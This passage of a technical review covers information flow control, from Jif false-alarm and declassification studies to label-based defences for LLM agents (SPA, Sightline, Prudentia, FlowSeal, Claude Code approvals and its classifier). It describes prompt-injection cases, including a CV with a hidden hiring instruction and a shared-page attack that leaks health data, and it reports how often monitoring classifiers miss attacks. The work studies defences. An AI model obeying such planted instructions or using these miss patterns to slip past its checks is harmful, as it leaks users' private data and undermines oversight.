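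Only 17 of the alarms concerned explicit flows, and all 17 were real. The other 870 concerned implicit flows, and 725 of those were false.

### Why a missing object sets off an alarm

Most of the false alarms involve exceptions, which are errors that interrupt a program while it runs. Take a login server that keeps a private record of the keys it has accepted:

```
1   if key in acceptedKeys:     // a secret condition
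2       history.add(key)        // history is secret too
3   reply = "finished"          // the visitor sees this
```

Line 2 puts secret data into a secret list, which breaks no rule. But a Java variable can be null, meaning it refers to no object, and calling a method on it causes a null-pointer exception. If `history` were null, the server would crash when it accepted a key and keep running when it rejected one, so a visitor could tell whether a key had been accepted. The checker has to report a leak unless it can prove that `history` is never null.

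The programmer may know that `history` is never null, because the server creates the list when it starts. Jif's checker can't prove this, since it tracks nulls only in the local variables of one method, and `history` is a field of the object. A better checker would prove more cases, but no checker can settle them all. In one 17-line stretch of the DES code, nearly every line set off an alarm. King and colleagues established by hand that none of them could fail, but an automatic proof would require the contents of several fixed tables and the possible range of each variable.

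One doubtful line also leads to more alarms. If line 2 might crash, then reaching line 3 reveals that it didn't, so pc has to stay secret after the branch. From then on, every exception the rest of the program might throw counts as another possible leak.

| Cause of the alarm | Alarms | False alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Null pointer | 475 | 455 |
| Array index out of range | 233 | 204 |
| Object of the wrong class | 24 | 22 |
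| Negative array size | 20 | 20 |
| Arithmetic error | 5 | 5 |
| All five unchecked exceptions | 757 | 706 |
| Ordinary branches | 46 | 14 |

Java calls the first five kinds "unchecked" because its compiler doesn't make programmers handle them. The remaining 67 implicit alarms came from other exceptions, such as those that the code throws deliberately, which the researchers didn't count as false. (The breakdown leaves five of the 725 false alarms unexplained.)

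Some languages, including the one Flow Caml extends, have no null. Removing every null-pointer alarm from King and colleagues' results would have eliminated 455 false alarms, but about two-thirds of the remaining 412 alarms would still have been false.

Jif programmers often satisfied the checker with an empty exception handler, which lets the program continue if the error occurs. King and colleagues found 568 of these in the roughly 13,000 lines of Civitas, the voting system. In 429 of them, the programmer had named the exception `imposs`, for "impossible". If the programmer was wrong about any of these, the program would ignore a real error.

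### Most real leaks were implicit, and most of the work was wasted

Of the 162 real leaks, 145 were implicit. A taint tracker would have found only the other 17, none of them in the login code. But a developer who read all 870 implicit alarms would have found that five out of every six were false.

The real leaks were also less serious than the word "leak" suggests. An alarm counted as real if a secret could make any visible difference, however small. For example, the length of DES output depends on the length of the input. Some login code revealed that a username was valid, but only after the visitor had given the right password. King and colleagues deliberately did not judge how much the leaks mattered.

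They suggest reading the alarms from explicit flows first, then those from ordinary branches, then those from exceptions. By their figures, a developer who stopped before the exceptions would have read 63 alarms, only 14 of them false. That rate is tolerable, but the developer would have missed more than two-thirds of the real leaks.

This test favoured implicit flow checking, because the researchers chose code that handles secrets directly and that they expected to leak through implicit flows. Other code would probably produce fewer real leaks per alarm. The researchers thought false alarms "could well be" the reason most security tools ignore implicit flows. They counted alarms and didn't ask toolmakers about their decisions, so the study can't confirm this, but it would be hard to persuade anyone who had a choice to use a tool with these error rates.

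### How a compiler lowers the label again

Labels tend to grow more restrictive as a program combines data, until they block useful actions. Researchers call this label creep. It happens because a join in the lattice can raise a label but never lower it.

A typed language limits the creep in two ways. Each variable has its own label, so a secret in one doesn't make the others secret. The compiler also restores pc after a branch. In the login example, if the compiler can rule out a crash on line 2, pc is public on line 1, secret on line 2 and public again on line 3, so the server can reply. If it can't, pc stays secret on line 3 and the compiler rejects the reply. Many of the false alarms in the 2008 study were therefore a form of label creep, where the compiler couldn't prove it was safe to lower pc.

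### Why an agent's label stays up

A compiler can read the code between two variables and show that one doesn't affect the other, but no code describes how a model gets from its input to its output. Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026), in *GIF*, point out that any token (a word or part of one) may weakly affect any later token. Requiring zero influence would therefore rule out almost everything. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls label propagation through a model an open problem, and warns that giving the output every input's label leads to a "label explosion" in which every piece of data ends up with every label.

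In practice, a run's label becomes strict early. *APPA* notes that the label can change only a limited number of times. With the four labels in the bug-report example, the limit is two, so one untrusted result and one private result are enough to put the strictest restrictions on every later call.

For a single call, though, the cautious assumption is usually right. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) studied programs that insert values into a prompt and send it to a model, drawn from 2,103 families of open-source repositories. Only 12% to 14% of the inserted values had no visible effect on the output. But a programmer had chosen each of those values. An agent's conversation also contains results from earlier steps that the current step may not need, so the share of unnecessary labels could well be higher.

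### Splitting the work between agents

Developers can approximate the way a compiler restores the pc label by giving part of a job to a second agent, as Zhou and colleagues do with their sealed computations.

Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, examined how far this approach can go in systems with many agents. In their simulation, published in November, a task is a set of tool calls, some of which need the results of others. Each call belongs to one agent, and some calls return sensitive data. An agent that makes a sensitive call, or receives or passes on its result, has a high label for the rest of the task. They measure the harm as

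utility loss = (calls that introduce a high label or run under one) ÷ (all calls).

Suppose a task has five calls and the second one reads a payroll file. If one agent makes all five in order, the last four count as lost, a loss of 80%. The loss falls to 40% if one agent reads the file and makes the only call that needs it, while another agent makes the other three.

The agents' connections also matter. The researchers compared each layout with an ideal network that has only the direct links the task needs. With five agents making tool calls and four sensitive calls out of 20, the extra loss was roughly:

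| Layout | Links between agents | Extra loss |
|---|---|---|
| Mesh | Every agent to every other | none |
| Ring | Each agent to two neighbours | 3 points |
| Hierarchy | Through managers and a supervisor | 4 points |
| Star | Through one central agent | 5 points |

When a message passes through other agents, its high label spreads to them. A star network is the worst case because all the agents share one go-between, and once it has handled something sensitive, its label carries over to whatever it passes on next.

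Using more agents reduced the loss, since each agent's separate memory limits how far the label spreads. But it also gave operators more links to monitor. A mesh of five agents has 10 links, while a mesh of 20 has 190. Grouping the sensitive tools reduced the loss in every layout. For example, a company could have one agent handle all its banking data so that the others never touch it.

Even the ideal network lost many calls, and Gregory and colleagues conclude that design alone cannot prevent the loss. Their formula partly guarantees this result, because a sensitive call counts as lost even if it affects nothing else. When half the calls are sensitive, as in their tests with more agents, no layout can bring the loss below 50%. The formula also counts as lost every call made under a high label, although a real policy would allow many of them, such as reading a second payroll file. The simulator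 generates tasks at random and runs no model, so its numbers are more useful for comparing layouts than for predicting how much work a real system would block.

### Keeping only the labels that mattered

Another remedy is to work out which inputs the model actually used and drop the labels of the rest. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, do this in three steps:

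1. Run the model on all the documents and record its answer.
2. For each less restrictive label L′, keep only the documents that L′ allows, and calculate how probable the same answer would be without the others. Accept L′ if U(all documents) − U(allowed documents) ≤ λ, where U is a score that rises with the answer's probability and λ is a tolerance that the developer sets.
3. Choose an accepted label, run the model again on only the documents it allows, and return the new answer.

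In one example, a user asks how many people live in New York City, and a web search returns a trusted page and an untrusted one. Both give a population of about eight million. The model can answer from the trusted page alone, so that answer can be labelled trusted.

The third step makes this safe because the final answer comes from a run without the excluded documents, even if the test in step 2 misjudges which documents mattered or an attacker fools it. The choice of label is less well protected and creates an implicit flow, though probably a small one. The system examines secret documents before deciding to leave them out, so anyone who receives a public answer may learn that the secrets made little difference.

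Siddiqui and colleagues tested the method with two Llama 2 models, which are now very old. They wrote 40 agent conversations, and a less restrictive label was possible in 20 of them. The method found that label in 17 of the 20 with the smaller model and 19 with the larger. A harder test had 3,465 questions about pairs of trusted and untrusted news articles. Even a perfect method could have improved the label on only 647 of them, because the rest needed the untrusted article or had no unnecessary label to drop. When the system had retrieved all the relevant articles, the method improved the label on 57% of those 647 with the smaller model and 39% with the larger.

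The extra runs cost money, and their number can grow quickly when there are many labels. An attacker can also add distracting text so that the system never finds a less restrictive label. This doesn't break the guarantee, but it makes the agent less useful.

Štorek and colleagues measure influence in bits instead of rerunning the model. Their method estimates how much the output would shift if the model's internal representation of a passage changed slightly. In their main example, an applicant's CV contains a hidden instruction to recommend hiring the applicant at $200,000, and the agent follows it. They estimate that the instruction contributed 82 bits to the recommendation, compared with 27 from the employer's criteria. A policy could then block an action only when untrusted text strongly influenced it.

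Xu and colleagues found that this measure can be close to zero even for the passage that decided the answer, because small changes to the input have little effect when a model is nearly certain of its answer. Their tool, Sightline, examines the model's attention, the mechanism through which it draws on earlier text as it writes. Models also attend to text they don't use, so the researchers trained Sightline on labelled examples to recognise which text the model used.

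The researchers tested Sightline on recorded tool calls from AgentDojo, made by an agent that used the small open model Qwen3-8B. Sightline removed 50% of the unnecessary labels and missed 3.9% of the real influences. The next best method removed 38%, and six others, including the bit measure, each removed less than 16%. None of the 34 calls that carried out an attack got past an integrity policy that relied on Sightline's labels. Because the researchers replayed recorded calls, they didn't measure how many more tasks an agent would complete with fewer unnecessary labels.

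Sightline, with its 3.9% miss rate, offers a different kind of guarantee from Siddiqui and colleagues. It removes the label but leaves the data in the conversation, so each miss leaves some real influence unlabelled. Developers can choose the average miss rate in advance, but it holds only if future calls resemble the ones used to set it, and attackers have an incentive to produce calls that don't. Willison's objection to filters that catch 99% of attacks seems to apply here too.

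### Planning before reading

CaMeL keeps its context label low by planning before it reads anything. In *SPA*, Girrens and Wang (August 2026) describe a similar system that comes close to information flow typing, because the checker can examine a complete plan as a program.

SPA's planning model runs once per request and writes the whole plan in a small language with six kinds of step: retrieve a stored result, call a tool, query a quarantined model, show something to the user, branch, or loop. Before any tool runs, a checker goes through the plan and tracks a label for each value and a pc label, which it raises only inside branches and loops. It examines both sides of every branch, as Jif's compiler does. Variables set inside a branch disappear when the branch ends, so a plan can't use them to carry a secret out.

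The plan also prevents label creep between requests. Suppose an agent reads a supplier's invoice on Monday, and on Tuesday the user asks it to pay that invoice. SPA stores the invoice with its label, then shows the planning model only a description of what it has stored. Girrens and Wang tested this by splitting each AgentDojo task into several requests. With label checks on, later plans retrieved the stored results they needed from earlier requests about 90% of the time.

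The checks themselves were expensive. All these runs used GPT-5.4 nano, a small OpenAI model:

| Tasks | Label checks | Completed, no attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | off | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| AgentDojo | on | 29.0% | 0.0% |
| AgentDojo, split into several requests | off | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| AgentDojo, split into several requests | on | 35.3% | 0.2% |

On the original tasks, four of 949 attacks succeeded without the checks. Turning the checks on stopped those four and cut task completion by almost half. The checker rejected about 53% of runs before they started, usually because the plan passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted input.

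Some of this loss comes from SPA's design. Its checker rejects a call if even one argument is untrusted, whereas Costa and colleagues can set a separate requirement for each argument. SPA also stops after a rejection, so that nobody can keep adjusting an unsafe plan until it passes. Some rejected tasks may have had another plan the checker would have accepted.

In the Java libraries, the checker mostly reported flows that could never happen, and a more precise analysis could have dismissed some of those false alarms. But in many of SPA's rejections, the untrusted data really would reach the tool, and the user often wants it to. An agent can't pay an invoice without the account number printed on it, so no improvement in tracking would remove the "untrusted" label from that payment, and someone has to decide whether to trust the number.

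## Declassification and other exceptions to the check

Before an agent can pay that invoice, someone must decide to trust the account number on it. Researchers call this endorsement. It is the integrity counterpart of declassification, which permits the release of confidential information, and useful programs need both. Publishing a firm's average salary violates noninterference, as the login page's reply does. Sabelfeld and Myers, in *A Model for Delimited Information Release*, describe declassification as an "escape hatch" from rules that would otherwise prevent practical programming.

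An escape hatch can let out more than the programmer intended. Suppose a firm with two employees publishes their average salary:

```
average = declassify((ann + ben) / 2)
```

If someone adds `ben = ann` above this line, the same expression publishes Ann's exact salary. Sabelfeld and Myers call this a laundering attack. Their rule against it, delimited release, adds one condition to noninterference. For any two starting states s₁ and s₂, and every declassified expression e,

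s₁ =_L s₂ and e(s₁) = e(s₂) ⇒ C(s₁) ≈_L C(s₂).

If two starting states have the same public values and the same average salary, their public results must match. Suppose one employee earns 2,000 and another earns 3,000. Swapping their salaries leaves the average at 2,500, and the original program publishes 2,500 either way. The altered program publishes 2,000 in one case and 3,000 in the other, so it breaks the rule. A compiler can enforce the rule by rejecting programs that change a variable and later declassify it.

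The rule doesn't test whether publishing the average was wise. The firm has only two employees, so each can work out the other's salary from the average.

### What, who, where and when

Delimited release concerns only what a program releases. The lecture slides *Dimensions of Declassification in Theory and Practice* add three more questions: who controls the release, where in the program it happens, and when. Askarov and Sabelfeld answered all four for each of the 14 points where the main class of their poker program declassifies data:

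| Points | What | Who | Where | When |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Public key for signatures | Anyone | Start-up | Before the game |
| 2 | Public encryption setting | Player | Start-up | Before the game |
| 3 | Signature on a message | Player | Sending a message | Any time |
| 4–7 | Starting data for the protocol | Player | Start-up | Before the game |
| 8–10 | Encrypted, shuffled cards | Player | Drawing a card | During the game |
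| 11 | Whether decryption succeeded | Player | Drawing a card | During the game, once the player has the card |
| 12 | Secret encryption key | Player | Verification | After the game |
| 13–14 | Secret shuffle | Player | Verification | After the game |

The first two points release data that was never secret. For example, Java returns a player's public and private keys in one object, so the program labels the whole object secret and then has to release the public half. Points 3 to 10 rely on cryptography. A signature made with a private key gets the key's label, even though signatures are meant to be shared. Point 11 reports whether an operation on secret data failed, without the details of the error.

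Points 12 to 14 do release important secrets. After the game, the players reveal their keys and shuffles so that each can check whether the other cheated. Revealing them during the game would expose the player's cards. Jif can record what the program declassifies, where, and on whose authority, but it can't express the rule that the release must wait until the game is over.

Askarov and Sabelfeld wrote their own fix, a true-or-false value that can change only once, which they called a seal. The methods that release the keys open the seal, and the methods that play the game check that it is still closed. If the program released a key too early, the next attempt to draw a card would stop with an error. The opponent might already have the key by then, so the seal limits the damage from a premature release but doesn't prevent the release. The program also checks the seal only at run time, so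 the compiler can't guarantee that the releases happen in the right order.

### Keeping attackers out of the decision

A release can have a sensible answer to all four questions and still be dangerous if an attacker can trigger it. Here a visitor controls `urgent`:

```
if urgent:
    reply = declassify(record)
```

Robust declassification rules this out. It requires that an attacker can influence neither what a program releases to them nor whether it releases anything. The formal version compares attacks. Let c[a] be the program c under attack a. Then for any two starting states and any other attack a′,

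c[a](s₁) ≈_L c[a](s₂) ⇒ c[a′](s₁) ≈_L c[a′](s₂).

If an attacker can't distinguish two secrets with one attack, they can't do so with any other, so they learn nothing more by changing their behaviour. The compiler enforces this by requiring both the declassified data and the program-counter label (pc) to be trusted.

The login page fails this test as well, because the visitor's guess determines which fact about the password the page reveals. If the password is either "swordfish" or "bluebell", guessing "swordfish" reveals which one it is, but guessing "marigold" doesn't. To pass the compiler's check, the program has to endorse the guess before it declassifies the result, so it needs one exception for integrity and another for confidentiality.

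### What the exceptions in two web programs were for

Jif 3.0, the version that Chong and colleagues used for their web email and calendar programs, enforces robust declassification. The programs contain 180 annotations that declassify or endorse something, or about one for every 22 lines of code. Many belong together, because a programmer who releases a data structure has to release each of its fields. Chong and colleagues grouped them into 39 intended exceptions and sorted these by cause:

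| Code | Annotations | Intended exceptions | Access control | Needs of the application | Compiler imprecision |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Web email | 76 | 14 | 11 | 3 | 0 |
| Shared calendar | 73 | 17 | 12 | 5 | 0 |
| User accounts | 31 | 8 | 3 | 4 | 1 |
| Total | 180 | 39 | 26 | 12 | 1 |

Of the 26 access-control exceptions, 24 involve moving data into or out of a database. Chong and colleagues had labeled everything in the databases as readable only by the application, so any code that uses the data needs the application's authority. With a looser label, they might have needed fewer exceptions, but they would have lost that protection.

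The 12 exceptions in the next column exist because the programs are meant to reveal some information. For instance, when a reviewer approves an email, the program removes that reviewer's restriction, and the recipient can read the email once every reviewer has approved it. Adding someone to a calendar event shows them its details. A visitor whose login fails learns that the password was wrong.

Only one exception made up for the compiler's imprecision. It applied to an error message on a page for selecting users, which had an unnecessarily strict label because several parts of the programs shared the page.

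One in 39 is encouraging, but Chong and colleagues were classifying their own code, and they counted only declassifications and endorsements. Jif programmers have other ways to satisfy the compiler, such as the hundreds of empty exception handlers in Civitas. Askarov and Sabelfeld describe another, in which a programmer writes a library signature that gives the public half of a key pair a public label from the start, so the program no longer needs to declassify it. They point out that the flow is still there, but Jif can't detect it.

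### Exceptions that only silence the checker

Ching and colleagues found a worse ratio in four programs written with Cocoon, the earlier Rust library. They judged ten of the programs' 21 declassifications unnecessary, all of them in the Spotify client. The Battleship game also had two unchecked operations, which turn off the security checks for a piece of code.

These exceptions come from Cocoon's design. Code can read a secret only inside a specially marked block, and it may not call functions there that change anything outside themselves. Placing a ship changes the grid, so the Battleship code contains this line:

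```
unchecked_operation(grid[row][col] = true);
```

The grid is itself secret, so the line leaks nothing. The other unchecked operation picks a random number, which changes the internal state of the random number generator. In the Spotify client, ordinary library functions don't accept labelled values, so the code sometimes declassifies a value just to pass it to one of them.

With Filament, the same four programs needed 11 declassifications and no unchecked operations. Ching and colleagues judged all 11 necessary. They designed Filament and judged both the declassifications and the unchecked operations themselves, so an outsider might reach different conclusions, but the reasons they give for the unchecked operations are easy to verify from the code. Their translation of the Jif email client has another 12 declassifications, mostly where the client passes data to the network.

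We can tell the two kinds of exception apart by asking whether a perfect checker would still require them. The email program would still need a reviewer's approval to release a message, because that exception records a policy. Battleship wouldn't need permission to place a ship on its own grid. The database exceptions are harder to classify, because they follow from a label the programmers chose for extra protection.

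The compiler treats all declassifications alike, so a reviewer of the Cocoon version of the Spotify client has to read 17 of them to find the seven that reflect a real decision. The other ten also do some harm, because the compiler stops protecting a value once the program has declassified it. If a later change sent one of those values somewhere public, the compiler might not report an error.

### A prompt that asks the user to declassify

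A programmer knows in advance that a login page will need an exception. An agent's developer often can't know which exceptions a user's next request will need, so the software asks the user for approval when a check fails. Letting the agent send private data to a new reader is a declassification, and approving an action that untrusted text may have prompted is an endorsement.

Letting the user decide has an advantage over Jif, because the user can see the actual message and recipient, while a Jif programmer has to decide in advance for every future run. But the programmer decides once, and colleagues can review the decision. The user may have to make similar decisions many times a day, usually in the middle of other work.

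Microsoft's sample policy for chat channels prompts the user only when the context is untrusted and the message's label excludes someone in the channel. Suppose an agent has read something untrusted and then tries to announce a product launch in a channel with three members, but the announcement's label permits only two of them to read it. The user sees a warning that begins "Sending the message would declassify it to users with IDs", followed by the third member's ID.

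In practice, the policy sends every message that fails the label check to the user. Its last rule denies the message, but the rule before it sends the message to the user whenever the number of excluded members is at least zero, which is always true. The policy can therefore deny a message only if it fails to compute that number.

Microsoft describes this policy as robust declassification, but in a trusted context the policy doesn't check who may read the message. If the agent had read only trusted data, it could post the announcement to all three members without asking, even though the label excludes one of them. If an agent treated emails from Priya and Marco as trusted, it could likewise post Priya's sales figures in a channel that Marco reads. Robustness prevents an attacker from influencing the decision to release data, but it doesn't protect against the model's own mistakes. Microsoft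 warns in the same post that such a mistake can do anything a user's request can.

### How people answer the prompts

The best recent figures on approvals are Anthropic's, for its coding agent, Claude Code. By default, the agent asked the user before every file write and every shell command (an instruction typed to the operating system), according to *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026). *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accepted 93% of prompts. By August 2026 they accepted 97%, according to *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

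Most commands are harmless, so a high acceptance rate doesn't prove that people are careless. To find out how people respond to a harmful command, Anthropic had a research firm recruit 1,053 paid testers for what looked like an ordinary coding study. Partway through each session, the text of one prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

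The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a real user. Anthropic was also promoting a product that replaces these prompts. But even if real users were three times as careful, they would approve more than half of the dangerous commands.

Many users avoid the approval prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without approval, and many of these rules were very broad. For example, a rule that allows any Python program allows almost anything, because a Python program can delete files or send them elsewhere. A quarter of interactive sessions started with the prompts switched off.

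These users may still be supervising the agent. Digital Watch's *AI agent autonomy rises as users gain trust in Anthropic’s Claude Code* reports on another Anthropic study, which found that experienced users both approve actions automatically and interrupt the agent more often. They may prefer to watch the work and step in when something looks wrong. This can be reasonable for catching a bad design, but it is a poor way to stop a leak, which may be over before anyone notices.

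People also reject some kinds of proposals more often than others. Users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents for approval. Some of those rejections are surely about the plan's quality rather than its safety, but they suggest that people read a proposal when it covers a meaningful piece of work.

### Asking less often

Labels can reduce the number of prompts, because the software needs to ask the user only when a check fails. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, published in February 2026, measures this reduction and tries to increase it with Prudentia, an agent built on FIDES. Prudentia gives its planning model each tool's policy and the current context label, which FIDES doesn't, so the model can account for them in its plans. Before the model reveals hidden data to itself, it must give a reason and list the tool calls it expects to make next.

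Prudentia can also prompt the user to endorse a piece of data. Suppose a harmless but untrusted email lists ten tasks, each of which needs a tool that requires a trusted context. If the user endorses the email, the agent can complete all ten tasks after that one prompt. Without the endorsement, reading the email makes the context untrusted, and the user has to approve ten separate calls.

The single prompt carries more risk. If the user overlooks an attacker's instruction in the email, the agent will treat that instruction as trusted too, and later integrity checks won't stop it. Ten prompts give the user ten chances to notice, although the Claude Code figures suggest that people make little use of them. Prudentia still requires the user to approve each declassification, because whether private data should go to a particular person depends heavily on the situation.

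The experiments used AgentDojo tasks with no attack under way. With OpenAI's o3-mini, an older reasoning model, the results were:

| Agent | Prompts across all completed tasks | Tasks completed without any prompt |
|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Asks when a context label check fails | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

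Prudentia cut the number of prompts by a factor of 2.9 compared with the agent that always asked. But with o3-mini, nearly all of that reduction came from the labels and hidden variables that FIDES already had. Planning made a much bigger difference with o4-mini, where prompts fell from 36.8 with FIDES to 19.2 with Prudentia. Task completion fell slightly, from 75.7% to 73.2%.

On WASP, a benchmark of attacks on agents that use websites, Prudentia needed no prompts. The user's tasks were to post a comment or upvote a post, so the agent never had to read untrusted text to decide what to do.

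No users answered prompts in these experiments. The researchers counted a prompt whenever a call failed its policy check, and assumed the user would approve it if the agent went on to complete the task. The results therefore measure how often an agent would interrupt a user, but not how well the user would decide. Anthropic's testers approved about five out of six dangerous commands even early in a session, so fewer prompts probably wouldn't be enough to make approvals reliable. A prompt based on labels can show where the data came from and who would gain access to it. That could help, but none of these studies tested it.

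### A language model as the judge

Another option is to let a second model decide. In August 2026 Anthropic made this the default for new Claude Code sessions on several plans. A classifier reviews any action that the simpler rules don't already allow. It blocked 937 of the 1,053 dangerous commands in the tester study, or 89%. It is given the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but not the results of those calls, so text on an attacker's web page can't reach it directly.

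The classifier does less well on realistic mistakes. In an earlier evaluation, it missed 17% of 52 real cases in which Claude Code had tried to do more than the user authorised, and it blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly concluded that the user's permission covered the action. For example, it might treat a request to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) as permission to overwrite the project's shared history.

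Anthropic's classifier doesn't use information flow labels. Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, combine the two approaches in FlowSeal, a system for personal assistants that hold someone's private records. Software outside the agent's model labels the records by owner, tracks which of them the agent has read, and intercepts every attempt to write or share something. If the agent has read a private record and the recipient isn't already approved or banned, a separate model acts as judge. It sees only the private records and the proposed output, and answers "SAFE" or "BLOCKED". The rule for sending content c to a destination d is

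label(c) ⊑ label(d) or judge(c, d) = SAFE.

Some of the attacks tested against FlowSeal involve implicit flows. In one, an attacker creates a shared page that lists several possible facts about a man's health, some true and some false, and asks the assistant to delete the ones that don't match its records. The assistant writes nothing private, but only the true facts remain on the page. This attack revealed 75.6% of the private items when the defence relied on careful instructions to the assistant's own model, and 2.3% when the defence was FlowSeal.

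Shim and colleagues prove that FlowSeal never sends private content to an unauthorised recipient "unless" the judge wrongly answers "SAFE". So the deterministic part of the guarantee is that the judge always gets a say, and whether the data stays private depends on its answer. They also replaced the judge with fixed answers, which shows how much depends on it:

| Judge | Private items leaked under one attack | Ordinary tasks completed |
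|---|---|---|
| Language model | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always answers "BLOCKED" | 1.3% | 0.0% |
| Always answers "SAFE" | 24.9% | 79.4% |

If the judge always blocks, the labels stop almost all leaks but also every ordinary task. The remaining 1.3% is hard to reconcile with the theorem and may reflect errors by the model that scored the leaks. A model acting as judge makes the system usable by recognising which outputs are unrelated to the private records.

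That makes most of its "SAFE" verdicts different from a real declassification. If the verdict is right, the output contains nothing private, and the judge has only removed a label that the software applied too broadly. When the owner wants to share something private, FlowSeal has a separate procedure for asking permission, which worked less well. In a test where the owner would agree if asked, FlowSeal shared 32.7% of the requested items, compared with 61% to 86% for four other defences. Shim and colleagues attribute this mainly to the assistant asking for permission less often.

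The judge also doesn't enforce robust declassification. An attacker can decide when to ask and what to ask for, and FlowSeal relies on the judge to spot anything private in the reply. Keeping the judge out of the conversation protects it from most persuasion. But the assistant has read the attacker's messages and writes the output that the judge sees, so it might pass on text meant to influence the verdict. Shim and colleagues didn't measure this because they excluded prompt injection from their tests.

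FlowSeal leaked between 0% and 3.3% of private items across the tested attacks. Willison's objection to imperfect filters applies to it too. In the worst case, 3.3% of runs leaked something, and at that rate an attacker would have about an even chance of succeeding within 21 independent attempts. Real attempts wouldn't be independent, and an attacker who learned from the failures might need fewer.

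A system that refers its failed checks to a person has the same "unless" in its guarantee, and by Anthropic's figures, the person is a much weaker judge than a model. Replacing the person with a model may therefore make an agent safer in practice, but it gives attackers a fixed target. They can test attacks against the same model as often as they like, and one that works may work against everyone who uses the product. Anthropic's classifier initially missed 12% of the synthetic attacks that Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, tried on it, and still missed 7% after Anthropic strengthened it.

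## Using only part of the system

Declassification and endorsement loosen the check one value at a time. A team can also leave out whole parts of the method from the start, for example by ignoring implicit flows, labelling only some of its code, or guarding against a single kind of attack. Google and Meta run partial systems like this at a scale no security-typed language has approached. Ruby also had a partial system for years, but later removed it.

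### Taint tracking in Ruby and at large companies

Ruby's taint tracking was based on Perl's. Ruby marked data from outside the program as tainted, and programmers could call `untaint` on a value after checking or cleaning it. With `$SAFE` set to 1, Ruby blocked some operations on tainted data, even checking whether a tainted file name referred to a link.

In 2019 Naruse proposed dropping the whole mechanism in *Remove $SAFE, taint and trust*. Naruse wrote that some people had used it in the early days of web programming but nobody did any more, and that libraries that read input usually didn't mark that input as tainted. One of these is Rack, which passes requests from web servers to Ruby applications. Naruse wrote a tiny web application to check whether Rack marked a visitor's query as tainted, and found that it didn't. A website built on Rack could therefore have switched on taint tracking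 and still treated an attacker's text as clean.

The mechanism had also caused several vulnerabilities and took a lot of work to maintain. Benoit Daloze, who works on another implementation of Ruby, pointed out that every time a program joined two strings, Ruby had to check both for the mark. The only participant who reported using taint used it to track which objects had changed. Nobody in the discussion defended it as a security feature. Ruby 2.7 dropped it, after changes to about 25 code repositories.

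This is the clearest rejection in the record, because Ruby programmers already had the feature in the language they used. Naruse's complaint was that the mark was only useful if every library between the network and the application preserved it, not that it caused false alarms or that labelling took work. Once Rack didn't preserve it, application programmers had little reason to rely on taint, and library authors probably saw little reason to support a feature nobody used.

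Companies have also tried tracking flows without blocking them. Meta (2024) reports using code analysis and logs to build a graph of which data feeds which other data. This worked on a small scale, but people still had to audit many individual datasets, and the graph couldn't stop a bad transfer as it happened. *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* (Wang, Bangert and Kern, 2021) concludes that advanced static analysis of Google's web code was unlikely to be worthwhile. Dangerous data often passes through servers and databases, where an analyser loses track of it. The paper also cites research suggesting that developers are less likely to fix a problem if the warning arrives after they have moved on to other work. Both accounts come from teams that had built a replacement, so they aren't neutral, but both replacements block bad flows instead of reporting them.

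### Adding labels to old code gradually

Disney and Flanagan, in *Gradual Information Flow Typing* (2011), start from the observation that programmers usually worry about security only after a program has users. They wanted a program to gain labels a piece at a time, and to keep working at every stage. Their main example goes roughly like this:

```
salary = secret(58000)
text   = to_string(salary)      // old library code, no labels
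print(as_public(text))
```

Every value carries a label while the program runs, even inside old code. `to_string` received a secret, so its result is secret too. `as_public` is a cast, which compares a value's label m with a required label l and lets the value through only if m ⊑ l. Here the cast stops the program before anything appears on the screen. If the programmer moves the cast inside `print`, it protects against leaks from every caller, including unlabelled code.

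A cast never changes a value's label. It only checks the label or stops the program, so it isn't a form of declassification.

Later the programmer can declare that `print` accepts only public text, and the compiler will then reject some leaks before the program runs. Once the whole program has precise labels, it needs no casts and no tracking at run time. Jif requires programmers to label the whole program this way from the start.

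Casts on functions are harder, because nobody can tell in advance what label an old function's result will have. The language wraps the function and checks each call, once on the way in and once on the way out. If a check fails, the error message blames one side:

| Old function | Type that the cast gives it | Failing call | Who gets the blame |
|---|---|---|---|
| `to_string`, which may return secret text | Public number in, public text out | Receives a public number but mixes a password into the result | The old function |
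| `publish`, which accepts only public text | Any text in | Receives a secret | The code that called it |

Disney and Flanagan prove noninterference for every program in their language, however few labels it has, except that a failed cast can reveal about one bit per run. This is surprisingly strong for a partial method, but it has two limits. Their language has no variables that a program can reassign, so the proof doesn't have to handle the leak Fenton found, in which a skipped assignment leaves a label too low. And a value without a label counts as public, so the guarantee doesn't cover the salary if nobody marks it as secret.

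The programmer also loses some of the benefit of early checking, since a leak in old code crashes the program while someone is using it. Disney and Flanagan called the work "some initial steps" and presented a small formal language, so it provides little evidence of how well the idea would work for programmers. The idea has since reappeared in a system for agents, described below.

### A library in place of a new language

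Ching and colleagues blame custom compilers for much of the trouble with earlier tools. A team that adopts one has to rewrite its software in a special language, and someone has to update the compiler whenever the ordinary language changes. A library avoids both problems. It wraps each secret in a type whose contents other code can't read directly, and the ordinary compiler enforces that restriction.

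LIO does this in Haskell. In Rust, Cocoon lets a program open secrets only inside a marked block:

```
let z: Secret<i32, A> = secret_block!(A {
    wrap_secret(foo(unwrap_secret(x), y))
});
```

The block can open values whose labels may flow to A, and its result gets the label A. It can't change anything less restrictive than A, so whichever branch runs inside it, the public can't see any effect. Cocoon therefore doesn't need a program-counter label. The drawback is the ban on side effects, and Cocoon's Battleship game needed unchecked operations to get around it.

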